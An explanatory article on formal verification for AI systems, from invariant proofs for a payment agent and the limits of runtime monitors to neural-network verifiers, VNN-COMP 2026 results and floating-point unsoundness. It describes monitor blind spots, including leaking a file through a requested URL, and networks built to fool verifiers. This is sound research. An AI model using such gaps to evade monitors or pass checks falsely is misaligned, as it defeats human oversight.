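# Formal safety specifications for AI systems: what can and cannot be machine-checked about safety and consent

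## What does it mean to specify a safety property and check it by machine?

A formal specification states in a formal language what a system must or must not do. Formal verification means proving that the system meets its specification, with a program checking the proof. Unlike testing, which tries only a sample of inputs, a proof covers every input. Robert Floyd, Tony Hoare and Edsger Dijkstra developed the logic in the 1960s, but for decades even small proofs took a lot of work. The method now protects kernels, compilers, cryptographic code and authorization systems, including Cedar, Amazon's language for access rules (Tan, 2026, *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference*).

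Researchers would like the same assurance for neural networks, for the text that language models write, and for AI agents, which are programs that let a language model choose actions such as writing a file, sending a message or paying a bill. People can state some requirements for an agent, such as "never send a payment without an approval", in formal language with little loss of meaning. Other requirements are harder to formalize. For example, a machine can check that a record of a customer's consent exists and has not expired, but this check does not establish whether she understood what she was agreeing to.

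Any verification task starts from a model of the system, a model of its environment and the property to verify (Seshia, Sadigh and Sastry, *Towards Verified Artificial Intelligence*, 2017). The guaranteed safe AI research programme requires the same inputs on a much larger scale. The verifier checks whether the property holds and, if it doesn't, usually produces a counterexample, a concrete execution that breaks the property. A positive result is about the models, and it applies to the real system only as far as the models are accurate.

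### A payment agent as states and steps

Take an agent that queues payments and then sends them. Its state, at any moment, consists of three sets of payments: Approved, Queued and Sent. All three start empty. The agent and its customer can change the state by three kinds of transition:

- Approve(p) adds payment p to Approved.
- Queue(p) requires that p is in Approved, and adds p to Queued.
- Send(p) requires that p is in Queued, and moves p from Queued to Sent.

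A run is a sequence of states that begins with the three empty sets and in which each state follows from the one before by a transition. A state is reachable if some run arrives at it. An invariant is a condition that holds in every reachable state. The specification here is "every sent payment was approved", or in symbols

Sent ⊆ Approved.

Since sending a payment does not change the set of approvals, this also guarantees that the approval came before the payment. For simplicity, the model has no step for withdrawing an approval.

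The property is true, but verifiers can't prove it by listing every run, because runs can be any length and the number of payments is unlimited. They use induction instead. A condition is inductive if it holds at the start and every transition from a state that satisfies it leads to another state that satisfies it. An inductive condition therefore holds in every reachable state.

"Every sent payment was approved" fails this test. Consider a state in which payment 7 is in the queue without approval and the agent has sent nothing. The property holds because Sent is empty, but it becomes false if the agent then sends payment 7. Verification engineers call the starting state a counterexample to induction. It does not show a bug, because Queue(7) requires approval and so no run reaches that state. The induction step still has to consider it, because the step assumes only the property, which does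 not mention the queue. As Lamport (2024) points out when defining the term in *A Retrospective of Proving the Correctness of Multiprocess Programs*, an inductive invariant must remain true after a step even from states that no execution can reach.

The problem is easy to see with a single payment. The payment is either in or out of each of the three sets, so there are eight conceivable states. Six of them satisfy the property, but only five of those six are reachable. The sixth is the state above, in which the payment is queued but neither approved nor sent.

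The remedy is to prove more. Add the helper condition "every queued payment is approved", so that the claim becomes

Sent ⊆ Approved and Queued ⊆ Approved.

At the start all the sets are empty, so both halves hold. Suppose both hold in some state. Approve(p) only enlarges Approved, which cannot break either half. Queue(p) requires p to be in Approved already, so the queue still contains only approved payments, and Sent does not change. Send(p) moves p from the queue to Sent. By the helper condition p is in Approved, so Sent still contains only approved payments, and so does the smaller queue. The proof covers any number of payments and runs of any length.

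Finding the helper invariant is the hard part in practice. *SV-LIB 1.0* (2025), a standard format for exchanging verification tasks between tools, accommodates invariants that are true but too weak by letting a counterexample start in any state that satisfies the invariant, even if no real execution reaches that state. *CIll* (Su, Bu and colleagues, 2026) gives a small hardware example in which a circuit computes a + b + c in two ways and stores the results in registers d1 and d2. The claim that d1 always equals d2 is not inductive until someone adds that the intermediate registers also agree, r1 + r2 = r3 + r4. An engineer can see this at a glance, but IC3, a leading algorithm for finding invariants automatically, has to express it bit by bit, and the number of clauses it needs grows exponentially with the width of the registers.

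Su and colleagues therefore let a language model read the circuit's source code and the counterexample to induction, and propose the helper. Conventional tools then test the proposal and send it back with a new counterexample if it fails. They used this loop to prove that two RISC-V processor cores comply with a formal specification of the instruction set (with simplified stand-ins for the multiply and divide instructions), which earlier model checkers had not managed. A wrong guess by the language model only wastes time, because the final proof does not depend on where the helper came from.

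### Safety, liveness and comparisons between runs

In *Proving the Correctness of Multiprocess Programs*, Lamport (1977) divided the properties one has to prove about a program into safety properties, which state that something will not happen, and liveness properties, which state that something must happen. His first example resembles the payment queue. One process puts messages into a buffer with room for b of them, another takes them out, and the number of messages n must always satisfy 0 ≤ n ≤ b. As with the payment queue, proving this property requires extra conditions, which here account for a message that the first process has put in the buffer but not yet counted.

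Precise definitions came later. Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*, treat a run as an infinite sequence of states (a program that stops repeats its last state for ever) and a property as a set P of runs. P is a safety property if, for every run σ,

σ ∉ P ⇒ ∃i ∀β : σ[..i]β ∉ P,

where σ[..i] is the first i states of the run and β is any infinite continuation. So a run that breaks P does so by some identifiable point, and nothing that happens afterwards can repair it. For the payment agent that point is the moment an unapproved payment goes out. P is a liveness property if

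∀α ∃β : αβ ∈ P,

where α is any finite run. However badly things have gone so far, they can still come right. "The agent eventually sends every approved payment" is of this kind: an auditor who has waited a year for a payment cannot yet say that the agent has broken the promise. Put a deadline on it, say a hundred steps, and it turns into a safety property, since the hundred-and-first step without a payment settles the question.

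Alpern and Schneider proved that every property of this sort is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property. Specifications need both more often than it may seem, since an agent that never pays anybody satisfies "every sent payment was approved". Safety proofs rely on invariants, while liveness proofs need a quantity that keeps decreasing but cannot decrease forever, such as the number of payments still ahead in a first-come, first-served queue.

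Both definitions judge runs one at a time, and some requirements do not allow that. Suppose the agent can see the company's bank balance and also writes to suppliers, and the balance must not leak. One run contains the message "we will pay on Tuesday". Did the date depend on the balance? Nothing in that run can tell. One has to ask what the agent would have written had the balance been different. This requirement is noninterference: changing secret inputs never changes what an outsider can observe. Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, gave the general class its name. If T is the set of all runs a system can produce, then T satisfies an ordinary property P when T ⊆ P, that is, when each run passes separately. A hyperproperty **H** is a set of sets of runs, and the system satisfies it when

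T ∈ **H**,

so that the whole collection passes or fails together. Finkbeiner (2025), in *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties*, writes one version of noninterference, observational determinism, as

∀π ∀π′ : (l_π ↔ l_π′) → G (o_π ↔ o_π′).

For any two runs π and π′ with the same public input l, the observable output o is the same at every moment (G means "always"), even if the secrets differ.

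Removing some of a system's possible runs cannot make it violate an ordinary property, but it can make it violate a hyperproperty. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that freely chooses whether to output 0, 1 or a secret bit. It satisfies the requirement that the possible outputs not depend on the secret. If the system is restricted so that it always outputs the secret bit, it violates that requirement, although it does nothing that it could not do before.

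Checking is still possible because a violation of observational determinism is a pair of finite runs. One can build a system that runs two copies of the original side by side, then prove an ordinary invariant of the pair. Finkbeiner notes that machines can decide even richer hyperproperties for finite systems, but the computation required grows by a further exponential with each switch between "for all runs" and "there exists a run".

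### What a monitor can enforce

Besides proving that a system meets its specification, one can run it next to a monitor that watches each step and halts the system when it is about to break a rule. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) works out what such monitors can do in principle. The monitor observes only one run, so whether a run breaks the rule must depend on that run alone. It cannot observe future steps, so when it rejects the beginning of a run, it also rejects every continuation, including those that would have corrected the problem later. It must also make every rejection after finitely many steps. Any rule that meets these conditions is a safety property.

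A monitor therefore cannot enforce liveness. In Schneider's example, a monitor can stop a seller from doing anything except deliver once a customer has paid, but if the seller does nothing, there is no forbidden step to block. A monitor also cannot enforce noninterference, because whether information flowed in one run depends on what would have happened in other runs, which the monitor has no access to. It can only enforce something stricter. For example, a two-state monitor that forbids all messages once the program has read a file prevents leaks through messages, but it also blocks harmless messages.

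The result applies to monitors that can only halt a program, and these cannot enforce every safety property. They can enforce "nobody waits more than ten steps", but not "nobody waits more than ten seconds", because halting the program does not stop the clock. A monitor that can also hold back or insert actions can enforce some properties that are not safety properties.

Schneider also warns that the monitor must sit where the system it watches cannot tamper with it, and that it must see every relevant step. Both requirements matter a good deal for AI agents. A rule against sending messages does little unless its definition of "send" covers every way to send one. For an agent with a web browser, that would include requesting a page whose address contains the text of the file.

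### Four kinds of checker

If the proof comes before the system runs, there are four main kinds of tool to check it with.

A type checker reads a program's source code and either accepts it or reports a line where the types do not match. The programmer of the payment agent could declare a type ApprovedPayment, let only the approval routine create values of that type, and have the queue accept nothing else. Code that queues an ordinary payment would then fail to compile. One still has to trust the type rules, the checker and compiler that implement them, and the approval routine. The checker would accept a routine that creates an ApprovedPayment without asking anyone for approval.

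A constraint solver takes a logical formula and looks for values that make it true. SAT solvers handle true-or-false variables, and SMT solvers also handle types such as numbers and arrays. To check an induction step, the user asks the solver for a state that satisfies the invariant and a transition from it to a state that doesn't. If none exists, the step holds. Otherwise, the solver returns the state and transition as a counterexample to induction. *Large Lemma Miners* (2025) uses a SAT solver this way to check lemmas that language models suggest for hardware proofs. The user must still trust the solver and the software that translated the program into a formula.

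A model checker takes a description of states and transitions together with a property, and searches the reachable states for a violation. If the programmer had forgotten the approval requirement on Queue, it would return the shortest bad run: queue payment 1, send payment 1. Such a run is the easiest kind of answer for an engineer to use. But the number of states can grow quickly. The correct payment agent has 5 reachable states with one payment and nearly ten million with ten. Many model checkers therefore search only up to some number of steps or payments, which works very well for finding bugs but usually proves nothing beyond that limit. The user has to trust the tool, and also that the description matches the code that runs.

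A proof assistant, such as Lean or Rocq, takes definitions, a theorem and a complete proof, and a small core program checks every step. It can handle the payment agent with no limit on the number of payments, as well as far deeper mathematics, but someone has to supply the proof. Tan reports that published projects often needed three to ten lines of proof for each line of code, and that language models are now taking over part of this work. Languages such as Dafny and Verus are partly automated. Solvers handle the routine steps and the programmer supplies the rest, which is faster but limits what one can express. Anyone relying on a proof assistant has to trust the core, the axioms, and the definitions and theorem as written, but not the author of the proof, human or machine.

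The trusted base is everything that must be right for a proof to mean anything but that the proof does not establish. It always includes the specification. In the payment model above, the agent can queue a payment again after sending it, so a supplier may be paid twice even though the proof is correct.

A verifier is sound if every property it proves is true of the system as modelled. It is complete if it can prove every true property in its class. Either is easy to achieve alone, since a verifier that always refuses is sound and one that always accepts is complete. No verifier for programs in general can be sound, complete and certain to finish, so designers who want soundness give up some completeness. A type checker rejects some programs that would never misbehave, and a solver may run out of time. A refusal from such a tool is therefore weak evidence of danger. For example, a checker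 that used only plain induction would have refused the original payment property, even though it is true.

### Which words does a requirement need?

Someone must state a requirement in terms of things the model contains before a checker can start. The payment property needed only approvals, queue entries and payments, all of which a computer can record. The table sorts some other requirements by what they refer to. Boundary events are an agent's effects on the outside world as the formal model records them, such as a file write, a message or a payment.

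| Vocabulary | Example requirement | What the model must contain | What shows a violation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Numbers | The network's steering output stays within 30 degrees of straight ahead | The network's arithmetic and a range of inputs | One input |
| Boundary events | The agent sends no message after reading a confidential file | A record of every read and every way to send | One finite run |
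| Data flow | The bank balance has no influence on letters to suppliers | Labels for secret inputs and visible outputs | Two runs with different balances, the same public inputs and different letters |
| Probabilities | The chance of a collision in an hour of driving is below one in a million | A probability distribution over traffic, weather and sensor faults | A calculation over all runs; no single crash settles it |
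| Human states of mind | The customer understood the fee and agreed to it freely | Her understanding and her freedom to refuse, for which a model has only stand-ins such as a click or a signature | Nothing in the recorded state |

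## What can be proved about a neural network on its own?

A trained neural network is a fixed function. It takes a list of numbers, such as the pixels of an image or the readings of a sensor, and computes another list of numbers. It has no queue and no history, so a specification for it needs no runs or invariants. The usual question is whether

∀x ∈ X : N(x) ∈ S,

where N is the network, X is a region of inputs and S is the set of outputs that the engineers regard as safe. A single input in X whose output falls outside S refutes the claim.

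### Controllers and classifiers

ACAS Xu is a collision-avoidance system that tells unmanned aircraft which way to turn. Its developers at first stored the advice in a table of more than two gigabytes, then explored replacing the table with 45 small networks that fit into three megabytes. Katz, Barrett and colleagues (2017), in *Reluplex*, set out to verify those networks. Each takes five numbers: the distance to the other aircraft, two angles and two speeds. It returns a score for each of five advisories (clear of conflict, weak left, weak right, strong left and strong right), and the lowest score wins. One requirement is that a network never advises "clear of conflict" when the other aircraft is directly ahead:

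∀x ∈ Ahead : N(x)_clear > min_a N(x)_a,

where Ahead gives a range for each of the five inputs and a runs over the advisories. Katz and colleagues proved two properties of this kind for all 42 networks they checked.

They also tested the property that "clear of conflict" never gets the worst score when the other aircraft is far away and much slower. It failed on 35 of 36 networks. The failures turned out to be acceptable because the networks are strongly biased towards repeating their previous advice, even when that advice was to turn, so the mistake was in the property. For another property, a counterexample exposed a real disagreement between a network and the original table, and the developers planned to retrain the network.

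For image classifiers, nobody can write down which grids of pixels show a stop sign. Researchers therefore usually settle for local robustness, which requires that every input close to a given input x₀ gets the same label as x₀:

∀x : ‖x − x₀‖∞ ≤ ε ⇒ argmax N(x) = argmax N(x₀).

Here ‖x − x₀‖∞ is the largest change to any single pixel value, ε is the permitted change, and argmax picks the class with the highest score. The formula only compares the network's answers with each other, so a network that labels every picture "cat" satisfies it. A proof for one picture covers only pictures within ε of it. Even so, *Introduction to Neural Network Verification* (2021) notes that most work in the field up to then was about this kind of robustness for images. Many of the standard test problems are still about it.

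One can also ask for stability around every input at once. Checking this requires comparing two runs of the network, which Katz and colleagues did with two copies side by side, as one would to check noninterference. They managed this only for small networks.

### Bounds for a network with two hidden units

Take a network with one input x between 0 and 1, two hidden units and one output:

h₁ = max(0, 2x − 1)

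h₂ = max(0, 1 − 2x)

y = h₁ + h₂

The function max(0, z), called a ReLU, leaves positive numbers unchanged and turns negative ones into zero. Suppose the requirement is y ≤ 1.5. This holds because y equals |2x − 1|, which never exceeds 1. How could a program prove it without using that formula?

The simplest method is interval bound propagation, which computes a range for each unit from the ranges of the units before it. As x goes from 0 to 1, 2x − 1 goes from −1 to 1, so h₁ lies between 0 and 1, as does h₂. Their sum therefore lies between 0 and 2, and the proof fails. The bound is correct but too loose, because h₁ reaches 1 only at x = 1 and h₂ only at x = 0, and the intervals don't capture the fact that both units depend on the same x.

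Splitting the input range solves the problem. For x between 0 and 0.5, 2x − 1 is never positive, so h₁ is 0, h₂ is at most 1, and y ≤ 1. For x between 0.5 and 1, h₂ is 0 and h₁ is at most 1, so again y ≤ 1. The two halves cover every input, so the property holds.

A second remedy is to keep the bounds as formulas in x. If the input z of a ReLU lies between l and u, with l negative and u positive, the graph of the ReLU never rises above the straight line that joins its two end points:

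max(0, z) ≤ u(z − l)/(u − l).

For both hidden units, l = −1 and u = 1. The line gives h₁ ≤ x and h₂ ≤ 1 − x. Adding these gives y ≤ x + (1 − x) = 1, with no splitting needed. This method is called linear relaxation because it replaces each bent function with straight lines above and below it.

The lower line can have any slope α between 0 and 1, since max(0, z) ≥ αz for all of them. With α = 1 for h₁ and α = 0 for h₂, the lower bound on y is 2x − 1, which can be as low as −1. With equal slopes, the two terms cancel and the bound is 0, which is exact. α,β-CROWN, currently the strongest verifier, adjusts these slopes by gradient ascent to make the final bound as tight as possible. It is fast largely because linear bounds for many cases can be computed in parallel on a graphics processor.

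In larger networks, the gaps between the lines and the true functions add up, and even the best slopes may give bounds too loose to prove the property. α,β-CROWN then uses branch and bound. It picks a ReLU whose input might be positive or negative and treats the two cases separately. The ReLU passes its input through in the positive case and outputs zero in the negative case, so it is exactly linear in each. In the small network, splitting on h₁ is the same as splitting the input at 0.5. The β in the name refers to multipliers that include each case's condition in the linear bounds. The tool drops a case when the bound proves the property for it, splits the case again when the bound is still too loose, and stops if it finds a concrete counterexample.

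### Why the worst case is hard

With n undecided ReLUs there may be 2ⁿ cases, and probably no method avoids this sort of growth on every network. Katz and colleagues showed that deciding whether a ReLU network has an input that violates a given linear property is NP-complete. A claimed violation is easy to check, since one can just run the network on it. The harder half of the proof translates logic puzzles into networks. In 3-SAT, one is given a list of clauses such as "a or b or not c" and has to find true-or-false values that satisfy all of them. Write true as 1 and false as 0. Then 1 − c computes "not c", and

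1 − max(0, 1 − (q₁ + q₂ + q₃))

is 1 if at least one of the three terms is 1, and 0 if all are 0. Add up these outputs for n clauses, and the total is n exactly when every clause is true. A verifier that can tell whether the total ever reaches n has solved the puzzle.

A network's inputs can take any value between 0 and 1, so the construction must also force each one to be exactly 0 or 1. The unit that Katz and colleagues give for this also accepts intermediate values as printed. A simple fix is to require x − max(0, 2x − 1) to equal zero, which happens between 0 and 1 only at the endpoints. A verifier that was fast on every ReLU network could therefore solve every 3-SAT puzzle quickly, and P would equal NP.

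NP-completeness describes the worst case, though, and typical networks have become much easier to verify. In 2017, Katz and colleagues' tool took about 110 hours to check one ACAS Xu property on 41 networks, and it timed out on four more. At VNN-COMP 2026, the field's annual competition, three tools settled all 186 ACAS Xu problems within a limit of 116 seconds each. α,β-CROWN took about two seconds on many of them.

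### VNN-COMP 2026

Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026) report results for 13 tools in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*. Each problem consists of a network, a property written in the VNN-LIB format and a time limit. A tool earns 10 points for a correct proof or counterexample and none if it runs out of time. It loses 150 points for a wrong answer, so guessing raises its expected score only if its guesses are right more than 15 times out of 16. The organisers then rescale the points so that the best tool on each benchmark gets 100.

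α,β-CROWN won the main track with 2,344 points out of a possible 2,400. It had also won the year before, as Kaulen, Ladner and colleagues (2025), in *The 6th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2025)*, report. Vibecheck came second with 2,279, followed by PyRAT (1,814), NeuralSAT (1,726), NNV (1,150), CORA (1,056), Bright (1,001), n2v (985), SuperSimple (665), ACT (650), nnenum (489), SobolBox (451) and Agate (0). Vibecheck is a newcomer that a team at Stony Brook University built in two months with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent.

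α,β-CROWN settled 3,164 of the 3,373 problems in the main track, with 1,982 proofs and 1,182 counterexamples. The table shows its results on some of the benchmarks.

| Benchmark | Parameters per network | Proved | Refuted | Not settled |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| ACAS Xu advisories | 13,000 | 139 | 47 | 0 |
| safeNLP (sentence classifiers) | 4,000 | 418 | 662 | 0 |
| VGG-16 (image classifier) | 138 million | 18 | 0 | 0 |
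| Tiny ImageNet (image classifier) | 3.6 million | 139 | 38 | 23 |
| CIFAR-100 (image classifiers) | 2.5 to 3.8 million | 127 | 33 | 40 |
| Small vision transformers | 68,000 to 76,000 | 123 | 0 | 77 |
| Traffic signs (networks with mostly two-valued weights) | 0.9 to 1.8 million | 0 | 36 | 9 |

A network's size is a poor guide to how hard it is to verify. The tool proved all 18 properties of VGG-16, some of which allow changes to only a few pixels, but ran out of time on more than a third of the problems for transformers about 2,000 times smaller. Some of the difference arises because the benchmark's proposers had removed the transformer problems that older methods solve easily.

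Another benchmark uses networks that researchers trained specifically so that verifiers can prove them robust, which lowers their accuracy. On CIFAR-10, a standard set of small photographs in ten classes, one of these networks labels 57% of the test images correctly, but only 35% also have a proof that the label is stable under pixel changes of up to 8/255. A wider network labels 85% correctly, and 60% also have a proof for smaller changes of up to 2/255, but α,β-CROWN failed to settle 14% of the test images even with 1,000 seconds for each.

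#### Wrong answers

The organisers don't know the right answer to most of the problems in advance, so they count a tool's report that a property holds as wrong only if another tool produces a valid counterexample. On the vision transformer benchmark, ACT reported that all 200 properties hold, 77 more than α,β-CROWN could prove, and received full marks because nobody refuted any of them. All 200 may hold, but the benchmark's proposers had removed the problems for which a standard attack finds a counterexample, and they warn that the benchmark may therefore fail to expose unsound tools. ACT gave ten wrong answers on other benchmarks, so α,β-CROWN's 123 is the safer figure.

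Eight of the 13 tools had at least one answer marked wrong. Agate had 955, because a last-minute bug spoiled its counterexamples. NeuralSAT had 94, nnenum 58, SuperSimple 14, ACT 10, SobolBox 2, and CORA and α,β-CROWN one each. These totals include missing or invalid counterexamples, so an answer marked wrong is not necessarily a false proof. α,β-CROWN's error was on SoundnessBench, a benchmark proposed by its own team that contains problems with planted, hard-to-find counterexamples.

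A neural network verifier is a large program and part of the trusted base, so a bug in it could make its answer wrong. The organisers eventually want to require each tool to output a proof with every "holds" answer, so that a small separate program could check the proof, as in a proof assistant.

#### How large is large?

The largest network in the competition, VGG-16, has 138 million parameters. The largest language models with published sizes have a trillion or more, at least 7,000 times as many. The properties are also much narrower than anything one would want to know about a language model.

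Certifiers can handle larger networks if the designers build the networks for the purpose. The idea is to limit how quickly the outputs can change. Let m be the margin by which the winning class leads some other class at input x, and let L be a Lipschitz constant, meaning that the margin changes by at most L for each unit of distance the input moves. The winner keeps its lead everywhere within distance ε if

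m > L · ε.

For example, with a margin of 3 and L = 2, no input change smaller than 1.5 can change the label. The check takes one multiplication and one comparison for each rival class, with no search. But the bound L for an ordinary network is usually so large that the test certifies almost nothing, so the architecture and training have to keep L small. *LipNeXt* (2026) does this with layers that preserve distances, and reaches billion-parameter image classifiers whose certified accuracy was still improving with size. These classifiers are still a thousand times smaller than a trillion-parameter language model, and the method certifies only local robustness.

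### The network that runs is a different function

Most of these proofs are about functions of real numbers. Computers run networks in floating-point arithmetic, which keeps a fixed number of digits and rounds after each operation, so the result of a sum can depend on the order of the additions. In double precision, for example, the next number after 2⁵³ is 2⁵³ + 2, and adding 1 to 2⁵³ gives 2⁵³ again. Write ω for 2⁵³. Then

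((1 + 1) + ω) − ω = 2, but ((ω + 1) + 1) − ω = 0.

Numerical libraries order arithmetic operations for speed. The order can change with the processor, the library version and the number of inputs in a batch, and on parallel hardware it can even change from one run to the next.

*No Soundness in the Real World* (Szász, Bánhelyi and Jelasity, 2025) therefore distinguishes two kinds of soundness. A verifier is theoretically sound if its bounds contain the true real-number output, and practically sound if they contain every output that the deployed network can produce. Many verifiers round lower bounds down and upper bounds up at each step to ensure theoretical soundness. The sum above shows that this is not enough for practical soundness. A verifier that adds in the first order never has to round, so both its bounds are 2, but a machine that adds in the second order outputs 0.

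Szász and colleagues prove that if the deployed system may add numbers in any order, then for any standard floating-point format and rounding rule, there are inputs and an order of addition that produce an output outside the verifier's interval bounds. Linear relaxation has the same problem, because it reduces to interval arithmetic for a plain sum of constants. Sorting the numbers from largest to smallest before adding them doesn't always give the lowest possible result, and the researchers suspect that finding the worst order is NP-hard.

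To test real verifiers, they built versions of a handwritten-digit classifier that behave normally on some machines and wrongly on others. The results varied with the version:

- One version depends on numerical precision. Its accuracy is 98.11% in 32-bit arithmetic and 0.11% in 64-bit, or the other way round, depending on how the researchers set it. All ten verifier configurations missed the hidden behaviour.
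- Three other versions depend on the order of additions. The easiest to detect was right on 98.11% of images when the PyTorch library ran it on a graphics processor ten images at a time, and on 0.11% when it ran one at a time. All ten configurations caught it.
- Six of the ten missed a harder version, which misbehaved in one of the eight environments that the researchers tried.
- All ten missed the hardest version, but none of the eight environments triggered it.

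So verifiers can certify a network that is almost always wrong on the machine where it runs. These networks were built to deceive, and the evidence on ordinary ones is milder. Jia and Rinard (2020), in *Exploiting Verified Neural Networks via Floating Point Numerical Error*, used networks with normal robust training. They adjusted the brightness of an image until a verifier could only just prove it robust, then found a nearby image that the real implementation labelled differently. This proves that verified robustness can fail without tampering, but only for images chosen because the verifier could barely prove them robust.

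*Lipschitz-Based Robustness Certification Under Floating-Point Execution* (Murray, 2026) gives a better idea of how often rounding matters. Murray tested a formally verified certifier that does its own calculations in exact fractions. He searched for false certificates among the test images for three naturally trained networks and found none at the usual values of ε, only when ε was around a millionth or less. He then changed the weights so that rounding errors grew by about six orders of magnitude while accuracy hardly changed. The certifier still approved 9,549 of 10,000 digit images, and at least 24 of those certificates were false. On the CIFAR-10 network, at least 7.9% were false. Rounding is therefore mainly a danger when the network comes from someone the user doesn't trust, which is also a case where people would most like to rely on a verifier.

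The competition has faced the same gap. Earlier editions accepted counterexamples that violated the property's constraints by a small tolerance. This in effect changed the problem, so two tools could give opposite answers and both be right. Under the 2026 rules, the input must satisfy the constraints exactly, and the organisers run the network on it in one fixed software environment. If the output violates the property exactly, the counterexample counts and tools that claimed a proof lose points. If the output violates it only within a tolerance of 10⁻⁴, the tool that submitted the counterexample keeps its points, but other tools aren't penalised. Ladner and colleagues acknowledge that this makes the verdicts reproducible but still ties borderline ones to a particular implementation.

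### Closing the gap

One response is to fix the order of operations. Szász and colleagues prove that interval bounds are practically sound if the deployed network always adds in one known order and the verifier uses the same order, precision and rounding. A proof about the network then holds only for that configuration, and a library update may invalidate it. Libraries with reproducible operations exist, but *TAO* (2025), a proposal for checking network computations that vary slightly between machines, notes that these libraries are slower and take more engineering work.

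A second reply is to allow for the worst possible rounding. When a computer adds n numbers, the total error is at most

(n − 1) · u · (|x₁| + … + |xₙ|)

in any order, where u is 2⁻⁵³ in double precision. For the sum with ω this is about 6, so the result must lie between −4 and 8, a range that includes both 2 and 0. The bound is loose, but nobody has to find the worst order to use it. Murray extends this kind of reasoning to whole networks. His certifier requires the margin to exceed L · ε plus a bound on how far rounding can move the outputs anywhere in the neighbourhood. It rejects every certificate that his searches had refuted, takes milliseconds per image, and loses few valid certificates except on CIFAR-10, where extra measurements before deployment recover most of them. He checked the theory in Rocq, although the Python program that applies it is not verified. The method also covers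 only fairly simple networks, without smooth activation functions such as the sigmoid.

In principle, one could verify the network's program code directly, including how it rounds numbers. *Floating-Point Neural Network Verification at the Software Level* (2025) tested eight general software verifiers on 912 tasks of this kind. In the basic setting, ESBMC made no mistakes but settled only 162 tasks and ran out of time or memory on the other 750. CBMC settled 371 correctly and raised 121 false alarms.

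The most thorough response is to avoid floating-point arithmetic. Quantised networks store their weights and intermediate results as small integers, and integer addition gives the same result in any order as long as nothing overflows. Jia and Rinard recommend this, and Szász and colleagues see fixed-point arithmetic, which keeps a constant number of digits after the point, as a possible way to achieve soundness in practice. The proof must cover the quantised network, because rounding the weights changes the function. Finding a proof can still be hard. Nearly all the weights in the competition's traffic-sign networks are +1 or −1, and none of the 13 tools proved any property of them.

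## How does a proof about a network become a proof about the system around it?

The verifiers described so far check whether, in a single calculation, inputs in one range always produce outputs in another. Safety requirements for machines usually concern physical quantities and have no time limit. For example, a car has to stay on the road for the whole journey, and the concentration of a drug in a patient's blood has to stay below a toxic level however many doses she receives.

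Some tools analyse the network and its surroundings together. They start with a set of possible states, work out where the network and the physics can take the system in one step, and repeat. The approximation errors add up, so the proofs cover only a limited time, rarely more than a few hundred steps according to Daggitt, Komendantskaya and colleagues (2026), in *Compositional Neural-Cyber-Physical System Verification in the Interactive Theorem Prover of Your Choice*. These researchers split the proof in two instead. If N is the network, ψ a condition on the network alone and Φ the requirement on the whole system, they prove

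ψ(N) and ∀f : ψ(f) ⇒ Φ(system controlled by f).

A network verifier proves the first half. A person proves the second half in a proof assistant. The second half holds for any controller that satisfies ψ, so it doesn't involve the network's weights. The hard part is finding a ψ simple enough for the verifier and strong enough for the rest of the proof.

### A car in a cross-wind

A problem posed by Boyer, Green and Moore in 1990 shows how a proof about a network can become a proof about the system around it. A car drives along a straight road 6 metres wide while the wind pushes it sideways. The wind changes by at most 1 per time step, and a sensor reports the car's distance from the centre line with an error of at most 0.25 metres. At each step the network receives the current reading x and the previous reading y, and returns a change in the car's sideways velocity. The car must never be more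 than 3 metres from the centre line.

The condition on the network is

|x| ≤ 3.25 and |y| ≤ 3.25 ⇒ |N(x, y) + 2x − y| < 1.25.

To see why this is enough, suppose first that the readings are exact and the wind is steady. Without steering, the car would move as far in the next step as it did in the last one, which would take it to 2x − y. Steering shifts that by N(x, y), so the condition puts the car's predicted position within 1.25 metres of the centre. The current reading counts twice in the prediction, so its error adds up to 0.5 metres. The error in the previous reading adds up to 0.25, and a change in the wind up to 1. The car therefore ends up within

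1.25 + 0.5 + 0.25 + 1 = 3

metres of the centre. The next reading is then at most 3.25, so the condition applies again at the next step, and the next. Given a safe start, this is an inductive invariant, and it covers a journey of any length.

### The embedding gap

The condition above is in metres, but the network doesn't take metres. Networks learn best from inputs of similar size, so a short program first converts each reading r to (r + 4)/8, which lies between 0 and 1 for readings of up to 4 metres on either side. Write x₀ and x₁ for the converted readings and y₀ for the output. The verifier has to search for values of x₀ and x₁ between 0.09375 and 0.90625 such that

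16x₀ − 8x₁ + y₀ ≥ 5.25 or 16x₀ − 8x₁ + y₀ ≤ 2.75.

An engineer who knows about cars can judge whether the first condition makes sense, but she would have trouble judging the second, even though it describes exactly the violations of the first.

Daggitt, Kokke and colleagues (2025), in *Vehicle*, call the lack of a practical way to connect the two the embedding gap. Let e be the program that converts physical quantities into network inputs, and u the program that converts the outputs back. Besides the two halves above, a full proof needs the link

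∀g : Ξ(g) ⇒ ψ(u ∘ g ∘ e),

where Ξ is the condition in the network's own numbers and u ∘ g ∘ e means converting the inputs, running the network g and converting the outputs back. Network verifiers can't reason about arbitrary conversion programs. In a proof assistant, someone would have to write out Ξ by hand, which is hopeless for a network with thousands of inputs. The usual practice has been to write the specification three times, for the training software, the verifier and the proof assistant, and to trust that the versions match.

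Conversion can also create inputs that mean nothing. *Neural Network Verification is a Programming Language Challenge* (Cordeiro, Daggitt and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a yes-or-no answer that the network receives as 0 or 1. Checking the two values separately doubles the number of cases with every such input, so people often let the verifier consider every value from 0 to 1. It may then report a counterexample at 0.97, which is neither yes nor no.

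### Languages for specifications

VNN-LIB, the format that the annual verification competition uses, expresses properties in terms of the network's input and output values. A version 1.0 file calls the inputs X0, X1 and so on and the outputs Y0, Y1 and so on, and lists constraints on them. The solver searches for values that satisfy all the constraints, so the file has to describe a violation of the requirement. Cordeiro and colleagues point out that the one-line definition of robustness becomes a couple of thousand lines for a simple image classifier.

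*VNN-LIB 2.0* (Roy, Antony and colleagues, 2026) lists four faults in the old version. It had no exact grammar, so different tools accepted incompatible files. It could describe only one network, with one input and one output. Authors could not state what kind of numbers the solver should use. And nobody had defined exactly which mathematical question a file stands for, so nobody could prove that a tool answers it correctly.

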